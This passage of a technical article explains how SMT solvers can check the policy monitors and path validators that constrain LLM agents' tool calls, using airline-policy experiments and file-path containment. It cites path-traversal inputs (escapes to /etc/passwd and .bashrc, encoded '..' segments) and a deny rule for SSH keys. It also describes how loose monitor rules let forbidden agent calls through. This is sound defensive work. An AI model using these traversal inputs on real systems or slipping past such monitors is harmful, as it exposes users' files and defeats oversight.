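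Meijer's remedy is to add to the tool's contract that files outside the pattern stay unchanged, after which, according to the article, the `*.txt` plan fails verification. That addition isn't enough. A file named `notes.txt` matches the pattern, so the new clause doesn't protect it, and the request still demands only that two files disappear. To reject the plan, the request needs a frame condition of its own: every file other than `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` stays as it was. The solver can then look for a file that breaks this condition:

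```
(declare-const f String)              ; any file name
(declare-const before Bool)           ; f exists before the call
(declare-const after Bool)            ; f exists after the call

; contract of the tool when the pattern is *.txt
(assert (= after (and before (not (str.suffixof ".txt" f)))))

; the request's frame condition fails for f
(assert (distinct f "foo.txt" "bar.txt"))
(assert (distinct before after))
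(check-sat)                           ; sat: e.g. f = "notes.txt"
```

One unknown file is enough for the query because the tool treats each file independently. If the plan instead deletes the two files by name, then under the contract `f` survives unless it is `foo.txt` or `bar.txt`, and the solver returns `unsat`. This proof needs the frame condition that Meijer added to the tool. Without it, the contract for deleting `foo.txt` would allow `notes.txt` to disappear too, and the verifier would reject a harmless plan.

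### Four attempts at an airline's policy

In *Solver-Aided Verification of Policy Compliance in Tool-Augmented LLM Agents*, Winston, Winston and Just (2026) had most of their trouble with the rules themselves. They built a monitor for the airline part of τ²-bench, which has 50 tasks, 13 tools and a 1,242-word policy document. They tried four ways of translating the document into SMT-LIB.

In the first attempt, a language model wrote the SMT-LIB directly, using an existing framework, Proof of Thought. The output contained syntax errors, undefined symbols and incomplete rules. In the second, the model used Z3's error messages to repair its code. The resulting 50 to 60 lines had correct syntax but omitted many essential constraints. Missing constraints don't cause errors in Z3, so the repair loop couldn't find them.

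For the third attempt, Winston and colleagues used AWS's Automated Reasoning tool, which produced around 600 lines. A language model judge estimated that they covered about 95 percent of the policy, but many rules were too loose. For example, the cancellation rule allowed customers to cancel within 24 hours of booking but didn't prohibit later cancellations.

The fourth design kept the AWS tool, added instructions asking for tighter constraints, and relied on people to review and correct the result. These reviewers defined missing variables, added conversions for timestamps and simplified declarations. They also ran the benchmark to find rules that let too much through, and repaired those. Winston and colleagues evaluated this version on the same benchmark, so the results may be better than they would be on new tasks.

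### Why a booking 30 hours old gets through

Winston and colleagues' monitor adds the facts of the case to the policy, asserts that the policy permits the call, and asks Z3 whether all of this can be true together. If the answer is `sat`, the call runs. Here is the loose cancellation rule with a booking made 30 hours ago:

```
(declare-const hours Real)               ; hours since booking
(declare-const may-cancel Bool)
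(assert (>= hours 0.0))
(assert (=> (<= hours 24.0) may-cancel)) ; the rule

(assert (= hours 30.0))                  ; the fact
(assert may-cancel)                      ; the call is permitted
(check-sat)                              ; sat, so the call runs
```

The symbol `=>` means "if … then". An if-then statement is true whenever its condition is false, and here the condition is false because 30 is greater than 24. The solver can therefore set `may-cancel` to either true or false, and the monitor accepts the value that lets the call through. A person reads "you may cancel within 24 hours" as also ruling out cancelling later, but the formula doesn't include that restriction.

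One repair is to write the rule as "if and only if":

```
(assert (= may-cancel (<= hours 24.0)))
```

At 30 hours, `may-cancel` must now be false, so the query returns `unsat` and the monitor blocks the call. The author has to put every reason for allowing cancellation in this one rule. If the airline also lets customers cancel when it has changed the flight's schedule, the author must add that condition to the right-hand side with "or". Two separate if-and-only-if rules would contradict each other whenever only one of the reasons applied.

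The other repair keeps the if-then rule and reverses the query. The monitor asserts `(not may-cancel)` and allows the call only if the answer is `unsat`, which means that permission holds in every situation consistent with the policy and the facts. For a booking 10 hours old, the rule forces `may-cancel` to be true, so the answer is `unsat` and the call runs. At 30 hours, the solver can set `may-cancel` to false, so the monitor blocks the call.

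The two repairs behave differently when a fact is missing. Suppose the reservation system doesn't return the booking time, so the formula has no value for `hours`:

| Form of the rule | The monitor allows the call if permission is | 10 hours old | 30 hours old | Age missing |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| If-then | satisfiable | allow | allow | allow |
| If and only if | satisfiable | allow | block | allow |
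| If-then | entailed | allow | block | block |
| If and only if | entailed | allow | block | block |

When a value is missing and permission only has to be satisfiable, the solver can pick a value that allows the call, such as 10 hours. Only the entailment query fails closed, meaning that it blocks the call when information is missing, because it requires the policy to permit the call for every possible value.

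Entailment works only if the policy states what is allowed. If the airline's document contains only the rule "no cancellations after 24 hours", the formula never forces `may-cancel` to be true, and a monitor that requires entailment will block every cancellation. The same choice arises without a solver. In Yu and colleagues' monitor, a rule can be a precondition, which blocks a call until some fact holds, or a prohibition, which blocks a call while some fact holds. If the fact is missing, a precondition blocks the call and a prohibition lets it through, so the system defaults to preconditions for rules about confirmation and authorization.

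In *A Neurosymbolic Approach to Natural Language Formalization and Verification*, An, Bayless and colleagues explain that AWS's service marks a claim as Valid only if the policy and the stated premises entail it. It marks a claim that is merely consistent with them as Satisfiable, which doesn't count as approval. With the loose rule, the claim that a customer may cancel after 30 hours would be Satisfiable. AWS also recommends the if-then form for almost all rules. The loophole arose because Winston and colleagues combined this form with a monitor that allows anything satisfiable.

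### What the airline experiment found

In the experiment, GPT-4.1 played both the agent and the customer. When the monitor blocked a call, the agent received an unsatisfiable core as an explanation and could revise its plan up to three times. Winston and colleagues ran every task four times with the monitor and four times without it.

The monitor reduced the share of the agent's write calls (calls that change data) that were invalid from about half to 29 percent. But the agent also made fewer correct write calls, and its success rate over all tasks rose only slightly. The monitor had a clearer effect on consistency, which the benchmark measures with pass^k, the probability that an agent succeeds in all of k independent attempts at a task. An agent with an 80 percent chance on every task would have a pass^4 of 41 percent. As k rose from 1 to 4, pass^k fell by 26 percent with the monitor and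 by 40 percent without it.

29 percent of the write calls were still invalid after a solver had checked them. A formula may still have been too loose, and some of the calls may have obeyed the policy without being what the task required. The solver may also have received false facts, because a language model, GPT-4o, read the conversation and the call's arguments and filled in the values that the formula needed. If it enters 3 hours for a booking that is 30 hours old, the cancellation passes under both forms of the rule and both directions of the query. Winston and colleagues do not separate these causes.

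The experiment also doesn't compare the solver with ordinary code that evaluates the same rules. Such code would give the same answers when every fact is known, so the gain in consistency is evidence for checking calls against precise rules, whether or not a solver does the checking.

### Testing a rule before using it

A short list of test cases for the cancellation rule would include bookings 10 and 24 hours old, which the monitor must allow, bookings 25 and 30 hours old, which it must block, and a case without a booking time. The tests should use the same query as the monitor, because the loose rule passes all five when the query checks for entailment but fails three when it checks only for satisfiability.

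Such a list can be short. In *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?* (2026), a language model translated the same airline policy into 16 prohibitions in a single call, and these gave the expected answer in 32 of 33 hand-written cases. This is a much better start than the first two attempts by Winston and colleagues, but the 33 cases cover only situations their author thought of.

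A solver can also run two tests that need no expected values. As in Cedar Analysis, it can search for a case that the rule permits and a case that it refuses. A rule that lacks either is almost certainly a mistake. The loose cancellation rule passes both tests, because the solver can return a 10-hour-old booking with permission and a 30-hour-old one without it, so the hand-written case with 30 hours is still necessary.

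Contradictory rules are harder to detect, because they may conflict only in certain situations. An and colleagues found an example when they translated the airline Ryanair's refund policy. An early passage denies a refund to passengers who did not travel although the flight operated. A later passage grants one to passengers whom the airline denied boarding. In simplified form:

```
(declare-const operated Bool)
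(declare-const travelled Bool)
(declare-const denied-boarding Bool)
(declare-const refund Bool)
(assert (=> (and operated (not travelled)) (not refund)))
(assert (=> denied-boarding refund))
(check-sat)                              ; sat

(assert (and operated (not travelled) denied-boarding))
(check-sat)                              ; unsat
```

The rules conflict only when someone is denied boarding on a flight that operates, so checking the policy by itself doesn't reveal the problem. A systematic test therefore takes each pair of rules with opposite conclusions and checks whether their conditions can hold together, both with and without the rules. The rules conflict if the conditions can hold together without them but not with them.

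A conflict like this is dangerous in a monitor that relies on entailment. Such a monitor allows a call when its query is `unsat`, and contradictory assumptions make every query `unsat`, so it would grant any request about the passenger who was denied boarding. A monitor that allows whatever is satisfiable would block all of those requests instead. The consistency check therefore has to run before every call and include the facts of the case. AWS's service does this and returns Impossible when the premises contradict the policy. AWS warns that if rules conflict in every situation, every request returns Impossible.

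Writing the exception into the general rule corrects this. The rule then denies a refund only to passengers who did not travel and whom the airline did not turn away. A human reader assumes that a specific passage overrides a general one, but all rules in a set of assertions apply at once.

### How reliable automatic translation is

Automatic translation would be most useful for long policies. AWS's service splits a document into short passages. A language model turns each passage into variables and rules, and the service merges variables that appear to mean the same thing. From a 274-page document, it produced 1,968 variables and 1,467 rules. People can inspect the rules as SMT-LIB or structured English and write test questions. The service can also use the solver to generate test cases.

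The service checks written answers, such as those of a customer-service chatbot, rather than tool calls. It translates each answer into premises and a conclusion, normally with three language models, and uses a solver to compare the translations. If they don't all agree, it doesn't approve the answer. The solver can catch mistakes that a language model misses. In An and colleagues' example, a park charges seniors $35.75 in the low season, and a chatbot tells a senior with $35.40 that this isn't enough. Claude Sonnet 3.7 and Claude Opus 4.1 accepted the answer. The solver found that the visitor can get in for about $35.34 by buying $15 of park credit for $9, even though using credit reduces the senior discount.

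An and colleagues tested the service on 563 question-and-answer pairs, three times each, with policies that nobody had corrected by hand. They report a "soundness" of 99.4 percent, which they define as the share of all decisions that were not false approvals. There were 10 false approvals in 1,689 decisions. But only 179 of those decisions were approvals, so about one approval in eighteen was wrong. The service also recognised only 14.9 percent of the correct answers. A checker that never approved anything would have a soundness of 100 percent, and An and colleagues acknowledge that the measure rewards abstention.

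| Method | Soundness | Correct answers approved | Approvals that were wrong |
|---|---|---|---|
| AWS's service, three translations must agree | 99.4% | 14.9% | 5.6% |
| AWS's service, one translation | 98.4% | 28.0% | 7.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 as judge, without a solver | 97.9% | 35.4% | 8.0% |

Most of the gain in soundness over the language model alone comes from approving fewer cases. This may be a good trade-off for a chatbot that can pass doubtful cases to a person. An agent that needed a person's approval before every tool call would hardly finish anything.

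In the Ryanair case, several hours of human correction to the rules cut false approvals in a set of 62 tests from two to none and raised the share of correct answers that the service approved from 25 to 45.5 percent. The set is small, and the team had used about two-thirds of the tests during the correction. AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails add new policy refinement workflows* (2026) describes a feature, added in June 2026, that automates part of this work by improving a policy using tests the customer has written. Customers would be wise to hold some tests back, since a policy revised until it passes a list of cases may still be wrong about others.

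### Checking drafted rules without a solver

Yu and colleagues restrict what the language model can write. People first prepare a vocabulary of conditions, such as "the cabin is basic economy", each with ordinary code that evaluates it. The model only links sentences in the policy to these conditions and to tools. A compiler then compares names to look for rules that cannot work. It checks which arguments each tool accepts, which arguments each condition needs, and which tools can make a condition true. This takes milliseconds and needs no solver.

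The compiler found these defects in the rules that a 26-billion-parameter model drafted for the airline and shop policies of τ²-bench:

| Defect in a drafted rule | Airline (79 drafts) | Shop (53 drafts) |
|---|---|---|
| Blocks the tool needed to satisfy it | 0 | 4 |
| Demands confirmation for tools that only read data | 5 | 0 |
| Needs an argument that the tool doesn't have | 8 | 1 |
| Needs a fact that no tool can establish | 5 | 0 |
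| Covers all tools without a usable scope | 11 | 2 |
| Total | 29 (37%) | 7 (13%) |

The shop's policy requires the agent to authenticate the customer at the start of the conversation. The model turned this into a rule that blocks every tool until the customer is authenticated, including the two lookup tools that perform authentication. Under this rule, the agent could never authenticate a customer, so every tool would stay blocked. The compiler repaired the rule by exempting the two lookup tools.

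Yu and colleagues switched off the checks for a second batch of drafts. Of the 14 airline rules that reached the monitor, 8 could not function, and neither could 3 of the 5 shop rules. A larger commercial model made some of the same mistakes. Even with the checks on, the compiler will accept two rules that each block the tool the other needs, because the checks examine rules one at a time.

Comparing names also can't catch a rule that works but means the wrong thing. In a third domain, telecommunications, the policy says to check that a bill is overdue before sending a payment request. The model produced a rule that prohibits payment requests while a bill is overdue, which is almost the opposite. Yu and colleagues caught the error by replaying recorded conversations from an agent without a monitor. In the runs where that agent had completed its task, the rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment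 requests. Replay requires such recordings and can only flag rules that the recorded calls trigger.

With the repaired rules, violations fell from 66.3 to 2.6 percent of the calls that changed data in the airline tasks, and from 30.8 to 6.9 percent in the shop tasks. Yu and colleagues counted violations with a separate set of hand-written rules, which avoids the circularity of Soteria's evaluation. On the airline tasks, the agent also made fewer calls that changed data, 116 instead of 353. Its success rate on a single attempt rose from 39.2 to 47.6 percent, which could be due to chance. The improvement was statistically significant when the agent had to succeed two, three or four times in a row.

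The 66.3 percent figure depends on how one reads a sentence in the airline's policy that requires the customer's confirmation before the agent changes anything. Yu and colleagues' rules demand a new "yes" for each change. If one "yes" may cover several changes that the agent has announced together, the rate without a monitor drops to 36.8 percent. The policy's author would have to decide which reading is right.

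One way to find translation errors is to produce two formulas and compare them with a solver. In *Faithful Autoformalization via Roundtrip Verification and Repair*, Amrollahi, Lopez and Barrett translate a legal text into logic, back into English, and then into logic again. If the two formulas are not equivalent, at least one translation step went wrong. *MANTRA* uses Z3 to search for a sequence of calls on which a model of the tools' behaviour and a set of rules for the agent disagree.

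Agreement between the model's rules and the hand-written ones is weaker evidence, because both can contain the same mistake. The airline's policy says that customers cannot modify basic economy flights, but a separate clause lets them change the cabin. The same tool makes both kinds of change, and the model's rule blocked that tool for every basic economy booking. Yu and colleagues examined 15 of this rule's refusals, and all 15 blocked attempts to change only the cabin. The hand-written rules blocked the tool in the same way, so comparing the two sets did not reveal the error.

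## Proving that a file path stays inside a permitted directory

Coding agents read and write files through tools that take a path as an argument. A team that wants an agent to work on one project will usually confine those tools to the project's directory, such as `/work/app`. But the segment `..` in a path means "go up one level", so `/work/app/../../etc/passwd` starts with the project's directory and leads to the system's list of user accounts. Using such a path to reach files outside the permitted directory is an attack called path traversal. The Common Weakness Enumeration, a catalogue of software faults, lists the underlying fault as CWE-22, "Improper Limitation of a Pathname to a Restricted Directory" (GCVE, 2025). The team wants path containment, which means that the file a path refers to lies inside the permitted directory.

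### One path, or every path

A monitor receives the actual path in each tool call, so it can check containment with ordinary code. *EffGen* (2026), a framework for agents built on small language models, resolves the path (works out the location it leads to) and allows the call only if the result belongs to a permitted set. The Python library for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools, does the same. Its `safe_join` function, documented in MCP's *path_security*, appends the requested path to the permitted directory, resolves the result and raises an error if it is outside that directory. With `/work/app` as the directory, `src/../main.py` becomes `/work/app/main.py` and passes, while `../notes.txt` becomes `/work/notes.txt` and fails.

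A solver can help with the checking code itself. Call a function that accepts or rejects paths a validator. Its author can test it on known attacks, but there is no end of possible paths, and the author wants to know whether the validator accepts any path that leads outside. The query has the usual form:

the validator accepts p **and not** p is inside

An `unsat` answer covers every path that the formulas can describe.

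### Three versions of a validator

The simplest validator accepts every path that starts with the characters `/work/app`. To find its mistakes, the solver also needs a formula for "inside". Split the path at its slashes into segments. If the first two segments are `work` and `app` and no later segment is `..`, the path is certainly inside, because every other segment either goes down a level or stays put. (Symbolic links, file-system entries that redirect to another location, can break this reasoning.)

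This definition can be written as a regular expression, a pattern that describes a set of strings. *Unicode Strings* (Tinelli, Barrett and Fontaine, 2020) defines the SMT-LIB operators: `re.++` joins patterns, `re.*` repeats a pattern any number of times, `re.diff` removes the strings that match one pattern from those that match another, and `str.in_re` tests whether a string matches a pattern.

```
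(define-fun name-char () RegLan            ; any character except "/"
  (re.diff re.allchar (str.to_re "/")))
(define-fun segment () RegLan              ; any segment except ".."
  (re.diff (re.* name-char) (str.to_re "..")))
(define-fun safe () RegLan
  (re.++ (str.to_re "/work/app")
         (re.* (re.++ (str.to_re "/") segment))))
(define-fun climbs () RegLan               ; has a ".." segment
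  (re.++ re.all (str.to_re "/..")
         (re.opt (re.++ (str.to_re "/") re.all))))

(declare-const p String)
(assert (not (str.in_re p safe)))          ; p is not certainly inside

(push)
(assert (str.prefixof "/work/app" p))      ; version 1
(check-sat)                                ; sat: e.g. /work/app-old
(pop)

(assert (str.prefixof "/work/app/" p))     ; version 2
(check-sat)                                ; sat: e.g. /work/app/../etc

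(assert (not (str.in_re p climbs)))        ; version 3
(check-sat)                                ; unsat
```

The first counterexample, `/work/app-old`, is a different directory whose path also begins with `/work/app`. Version 2 adds a slash to the prefix, which excludes that directory but not `/work/app/../etc`. Version 3 also rejects any path with a `..` segment, and no counterexample remains.

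With the added slash, the path `/work/app` itself no longer passes, although listing the project's directory is a reasonable request. If the permitted directory is `/`, the prefix becomes `//` and the validator rejects nearly everything. File-server code on Glama, a site that lists MCP servers, treats both as special cases.

Version 3 also rejects `/work/app/src/../index.ts`, which leads to a file inside the project. A validator can avoid this by resolving the path first and applying the prefix test to the result. The solver then treats the resolving function as a tool whose contract is that its output contains no `..` segment. The query about the output is the same as the third one above, so the answer is again `unsat`, but the proof now relies on the function satisfying its contract.

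Real code can break that contract. A bug report on Eclipse Theia, an open-source platform for development environments, describes a function called `normalize` that keeps a leading `..` in a relative path (zenniskayy (2026), in *[Eclipse Theia] Remote Code Execution via AI Agent-Mode workspace-escape file write*). For the workspace `/home/theia/project` and the request `../.bashrc`, Theia's path functions return `/home/theia/project/../.bashrc`. This string starts with the workspace path and a slash, so the prefix test of version 2 would accept it. The operating system then resolves the `..` and opens `/home/theia/.bashrc`, which is outside the workspace and contains commands that run whenever the user starts a shell.

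Another repair, deleting every `../` from the request before appending it to `/work/app/`, can still leave a `../` in the path. SMT-LIB's operator for this, `str.replace_all`, goes through the text once from left to right, as most programming languages do. Given `....//etc`, it deletes the one `../` it finds, leaving `../etc`. Microsoft's documentation for Z3 lists `str.replace_all` as unsupported, so Z3 can't check this repair directly. The solver cvc5 supports all of SMT-LIB's string operators, according to its *Theory Reference*.

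### The prefix mistake in released agent tools

Anthropic's filesystem server for MCP, which gives an agent such as Claude Desktop access to local files, used version 1 of the validator. In an example from Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Filesystem MCP Server*, a user who permits access to `/mnt/finance/data` also opens `/mnt/finance/data-archived`. The blog's author reported the fault to Anthropic in June 2025, after Elad Beber had done so, and version 2025.7.1 corrected it. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025), a record by Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates the fault's severity at 7.3 out of 10.

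The same mistake turned up in the file tools of CleverAgents, another piece of agent software. There, the change HAL9000 (2026), in *fix(security): fix file_tools.py validate_path startswith bypass*, replaced the comparison of characters with a comparison of segments:

```
str(target).startswith(str(root))   # before
target.relative_to(root)            # after: an error if target is outside
```

The old code had already resolved any `..` in `target`, but its check could still accept a path outside the root. With `/work/app` as the root, `../app-old/secret.txt` resolves to `/work/app-old/secret.txt`, which begins with the characters `/work/app`. The new code rejects this path because it compares whole names, and `app` differs from `app-old`. It still needs a resolved path, because Python's `relative_to` treats `..` as an ordinary name and would accept `/work/app/../etc`.

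The maintainers merged the change on 15 May 2026 with a test that may not detect the original bug. The test requests `../sandbox-evil/secret.txt` from a temporary directory. An automated reviewer pointed out that if this directory has a random name such as `/tmp/tmpABCXYZ`, the request leads to `/tmp/sandbox-evil/secret.txt`, which doesn't begin with the directory's path. The old code would have rejected it too, so the test would have passed before the repair. Another review by the same bot said that the test exercised the attack correctly. A test based on the solver's counterexample avoids this problem. The old code wrongly accepts `/work/app-old` when the root is `/work/app`, so a test that uses these paths has to fail before the repair.

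### Why "inside" needs its own definition

Whoever wrote version 2 may well define "inside" in the query as "starts with `/work/app/`". The query then only compares the validator's test with itself, because the solver has to find a path that both starts with `/work/app/` and does not. It returns `unsat`, but the validator still accepts `/work/app/../etc`. To avoid this, the definition has to come from how the operating system follows a path, and the programmer should write it without looking at the validator's code.

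The definition `safe` leaves out some paths that are inside the directory, so the query for version 2 could also return `/work/app/src/../main.py`, which is not a violation. An `unsat` answer is still valid, but someone has to resolve the path in each counterexample to see whether it is a real violation. No regular expression can remove all of these false alarms, because a path may go down through any number of directories and then up through the same number, and a regular expression can't count without limit.

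The exact definition processes the path one segment at a time and keeps a list of the directories that make up the current location. A name goes at the end of the list, `..` removes the last entry, and `.` and an empty segment change nothing. The path is inside if the final list starts with `work` and `app`. *A Simple and Intuitive Algorithm for Preventing Directory Traversal Attacks* (Flanders, 2019) builds a validator on this procedure. The validator accepts a path only if the final list exactly matches an entry in a table of permitted files.

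Resolving a path from its text alone differs slightly from what a file system does. In Flanders's example, `/home/NonexistentUserFolder/../ActualUserFolder/`, the procedure resolves the path to `/home/ActualUserFolder/`, while a file system returns an error because the first folder does not exist. This does not weaken containment, because the file system opens nothing.

### A depth counter

Many validators keep a number instead of the list. For a relative path, the counter starts at 0 in `/work/app`. A name adds 1, `..` subtracts 1, and other segments leave it alone. Two paths show which condition on the counter is safe:

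| Path | 1st segment | 2nd segment | 3rd segment | 4th segment |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `src/../../etc` | 1, at `/work/app/src` | 0, at `/work/app` | −1, at `/work` | 0, at `/work/etc` |
| `../app/x` | −1, at `/work` | 0, at `/work/app` | 1, at `/work/app/x` | |

A validator that checks only the final depth accepts the first path, because the path ends at 0, the depth of the permitted directory. But the counter doesn't record directory names. At −1 the path is outside `app`, and the next segment enters `etc` instead of returning to `app`. The correct rule is that the counter must never fall below zero, which rejects the first path at its third segment. The rule also rejects `../app/x`, which leaves the project and comes back. This is safe but stricter than necessary, and an agent rarely has a reason to write such a path.

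The MCP library's function `contains_path_traversal` applies this rule. It rejects `a/../../b` and accepts `a/../b`. It also accepts `1.0..2.0`, because two dots matter only when they are the whole segment. It reports no traversal for `/etc/passwd`, because its counter only rises, so the library needs a separate function to detect absolute paths.

A solver can prove the rule for paths with any number of segments, using induction. The author first finds an invariant, a statement that is true at the start and stays true after every step. Here the invariant is that the list of directories starts with `work` and `app`, followed by exactly as many further names as the counter shows. It holds at the start, when the list is just those two names and the counter is 0. The query asks whether a step that the validator accepts can break it. Z3's sequences, lists of any length, can represent the list:

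```
(define-fun root () (Seq String)
  (seq.++ (seq.unit "work") (seq.unit "app")))
(define-fun inv ((loc (Seq String)) (d Int)) Bool
  (and (>= d 0)
       (= (seq.len loc) (+ 2 d))
       (seq.prefixof root loc)))

(declare-const loc (Seq String))      ; location before the step
(declare-const d Int)                 ; depth before the step
(declare-const s String)              ; the next segment

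(define-fun stay () Bool (or (= s "") (= s ".")))
(define-fun loc2 () (Seq String)      ; location after the step
  (ite stay loc
  (ite (= s "..") (seq.extract loc 0 (- (seq.len loc) 1))
                  (seq.++ loc (seq.unit s)))))
(define-fun d2 () Int                 ; depth after the step
  (ite stay d (ite (= s "..") (- d 1) (+ d 1))))

(assert (inv loc d))
(assert (not (inv loc2 d2)))          ; the step breaks the invariant

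(push)
(assert (>= d2 0))                    ; the validator checks every step
(check-sat)                           ; unsat
(pop)
(check-sat)                           ; sat: d = 0, s = ".."
```

The expression `(ite a b c)` means "b if a is true, otherwise c". If the validator checks the depth after every segment, no accepted step breaks the invariant, so the invariant holds at the end of every accepted path and the path is inside the directory. The last query leaves out that check, as a validator does when it looks only at the final depth. The counterexample is a step up from depth 0, which is what the second `..` does in `src/../../etc`.

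The invariant is about the list of directories, while the validator uses only a number, so this proof isn't circular. If "inside" were defined as "the counter never falls below zero", the solver would again be comparing the rule with itself.

The sequence operator `seq.nth` returns the element at a given position. If the sequence is too short, Microsoft's documentation describes the result as "under-specified", which means the solver may choose any value. For example, if a formula compares the second element of a one-element sequence with `app`, the solver can make the comparison true or false. It can therefore report violations that no real path causes, unless the formula includes a condition on the length.

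### When two strings name the same file

To a solver, a string is a sequence of numbered characters, and two strings are equal only if every character matches. File systems and the software in front of them are often less exact, and the author has to decide how much of their behaviour to put in the formula:

| Requested path | To the solver | To the software that opens the file |
|---|---|---|
| `/etc/passwd` | Text to append to `/work/app` | May replace `/work/app` altogether |
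| `src//./main.py` | Differs from `src/main.py` | The same file |
| `/work/APP/x` | Differs from `/work/app/x` | The same file if the system ignores case |
| `café.txt` | Two strings, with é as one character or as e plus an accent | The same file on some systems |
| `%2e%2e/etc` | Contains no `..` segment | `../etc` if something decodes it |
| `..\etc` | A single segment | `..` and then `etc` on Windows |

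Absolute paths are the most dangerous case. In Python, joining `/work/app` and `/etc/passwd` gives `/etc/passwd` without warning. A formula that models joining as plain concatenation (`str.++`) would give `/work/app/etc/passwd`, so the solver would wrongly prove that the path stays inside `/work/app`. The MCP library refuses absolute paths before joining. The library documented in Docs.rs' *agent-sdk-tools 0.10.0* accepts them, and with the root `/workspace` it resolves both `/etc/passwd` and `../../etc/passwd` to a path under `/workspace`. Because this function never rejects a path, the query has to check whether any output lies outside the root. The drawback of this design is that the agent may read or overwrite a different file from the one it named.

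If a validator distinguishes spellings that the file system treats as the same, because of letter case or accents, permissions become too strict and prohibitions too loose. Suppose the validator is case-sensitive and the file system is not. With a permission for `/work/app/`, the validator rejects `/work/APP/x`, which blocks a legitimate request but exposes no files. But a prohibition on `/work/app/.env`, a file that often holds passwords, doesn't match `/work/app/.ENV`, so the agent can read the file. The solver will not find this flaw if the formula also treats the two spellings as different files. For a prohibition, both the formula and the validator have to convert the requested path and the prohibited path to the same form before comparing them.

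Software should decode a path before validating it. `%2e` is the URL encoding of a dot, so `%2e%2e` decodes to `..`. If decoding happens first, the validator can detect the `..` and refuse the path. If decoding happens after validation, the proof applies to a different string from the one used to open the file. An author who can't tell whether a later component decodes paths can refuse every path that contains a percent sign, though this also blocks a few legitimate file names. Zenniskayy recommends permanent tests to check that the validator rejects `%2e%2e` and Windows separators but still allows `src/../index.ts`.

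A backslash separates path segments on Windows but is an ordinary file name character on Linux. The MCP library treats both slashes as separators on every system. It also rejects any string that begins with a letter and a colon, such as `C:foo`, including harmless identifiers like `x:y`. LangChain, a library for building agents, has a function called *validateFilePath* that converts backslashes to forward slashes and rejects Windows absolute paths. The MCP library's string check doesn't account for Windows dropping dots and spaces at the end of a file name. The library's documentation says developers should use `safe_join` for real file access because that function queries the operating system.

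Backslashes also cause trouble in the query itself. In SMT-LIB, `\u` followed by four hexadecimal digits stands for a single character. If a monitor copies the Windows path `C:\work\ubeef` into a script unchanged, the solver reads the last six characters as one Korean syllable and checks a different path. Tinelli and colleagues' notation allows the monitor to avoid this by writing each backslash as `\u{5c}`.

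### Permission rules with wildcards

Teams often grant access with path patterns called globs, in which `*` stands for any characters within one segment and `**` for any number of segments. Lecture slides from UT Austin show a configuration of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, that uses the rule `Read(~/.ssh/**)` to block reads from the directory where users keep their login keys.

A glob is easy to translate into a regular expression: `*` becomes `(re.* name-char)`, and a final `**` becomes `re.all`. Each pattern then describes a set of strings, which logicians call its language. A grant stays within a permitted zone if the first language is included in the second, so that no string matches the grant without also belonging to the zone. Suppose the agent may read `/work/app/*/config.json`, and the team wants nothing outside `/work/app` and nothing in `/work/app/keys` to be readable.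 The query reuses `name-char` and `safe` from above:

```
(define-fun grant () RegLan                ; /work/app/*/config.json
  (re.++ (str.to_re "/work/app/") (re.* name-char)
         (str.to_re "/config.json")))
(define-fun keys () RegLan                 ; /work/app/keys/**
  (re.++ (str.to_re "/work/app/keys/") re.all))

(declare-const q String)
(assert (str.in_re q grant))
(assert (not (str.in_re q (re.diff safe keys))))
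(check-sat)                                ; sat
```

Exactly two strings satisfy this query. In `/work/app/keys/config.json`, the star matches the forbidden directory, and in `/work/app/../config.json`, it matches `..`. If the monitor resolves paths before comparing them with patterns, the author can rule out the second string by asserting that `q` contains no `..` segment. The first string exposes a real gap in the policy, which the team can close with a prohibition that overrides the grant.

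The translation has to follow the product's conventions. In Claude Code's file rules, one leading slash refers to the project's directory and two refer to the root of the file system (Anthropic, *Configure permissions*). With a project in `/work/app`, the rule `Edit(/src/**)` permits edits in `/work/app/src`, and `Edit(//src/**)` permits them in `/src`. Someone who reads the first rule as an absolute path will prove something about `/src` instead of `/work/app/src`.

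AWS applies the same method to access rules for its cloud services. Its tool Zelkova translates policies into formulas over strings, regular expressions, bit vectors and integers and passes them to several solvers, including Z3 and CVC4, according to SoS-VO's *Semantic Analysis of AWS Access Control*. In pretalx's *Stop Guessing and Start Proving*, speakers who built a simplified version of Zelkova argue that its formal guarantees are "likely unnecessary" for such policies. They may be right for a handful of file globs, because a library for finite automata, simple state machines that accept the same strings as the patterns, can check whether every path matching one pattern also matches another. An SMT solver becomes useful when a rule combines a path with other conditions, such as a user's role or a limit on file size.

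### What each encoding proves, and at what cost

The queries so far have used strings and sequences of segments. A third option is to limit the length of the path and cover every path up to that length.

| Encoding | What a "no violation" answer covers | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Strings with regular expressions | Paths of any length | Cannot define "inside" exactly |
| Sequence of segments, with induction | Any number of segments | A person has to find the invariant |
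| Bounded length | Every path up to the limit, with an exact definition of "inside" | Says nothing about longer paths |

The string encoding is closest to the code, since a validator receives a string. How hard a query is to solve depends on the operators it uses. According to slides from the University of Iowa, a program can always decide equations between joined strings, but nobody knows whether this remains true when constraints on length are added, and adding an operator that replaces all occurrences makes the problem undecidable. Z3 relies on heuristics that don't settle every string formula, so a query may return `unknown` or run until the time limit. Queries that only test one string against fixed patterns, like the ones above, are much easier.

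The segment encoding breaks the problem into short steps and allows the exact definition of "inside". But the proof covers only what happens after other code has split the path into segments. If that code splits only at forward slashes and runs on Windows, it passes on `..\..\etc` as one ordinary name, and the proof doesn't account for the two `..` segments in it.

A bounded encoding needs no invariant, because the formula can contain a copy of the location after each of a fixed number of segments, such as six. But if the limit is too low, the solver can miss a bug. Version 2 of the validator, which adds the slash but ignores `..`, is broken, and its shortest counterexample is `/work/app/..`, which has 12 characters. If paths are limited to 11 characters, the solver returns `unsat`.

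Flanders used KLEE to check an implementation in C, with a bound of 12 characters. KLEE runs a compiled program with unknown input and uses a solver to work out which inputs lead down each branch. Unlike the formulas above, it examines the program itself, so it can catch a typing error in the validator's code. On a laptop-class processor, KLEE took 323 seconds and found no input that left traversal segments in the output. The absence of these segments is a weaker property than containment, since `/etc/passwd` has none but is outside the permitted directory.

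In an earlier run, Flanders asked KLEE for inputs that the function turns into `/a/b/c`. It returned 1,142 in 137 seconds, mostly the same path with extra slashes. Flanders looked through the list and found no harmful ones. The verification code that selected these inputs also contains the prefix mistake. It compares only the first six characters of the output with `/a/b/c`, so it would count `/a/b/cd` as a match too.

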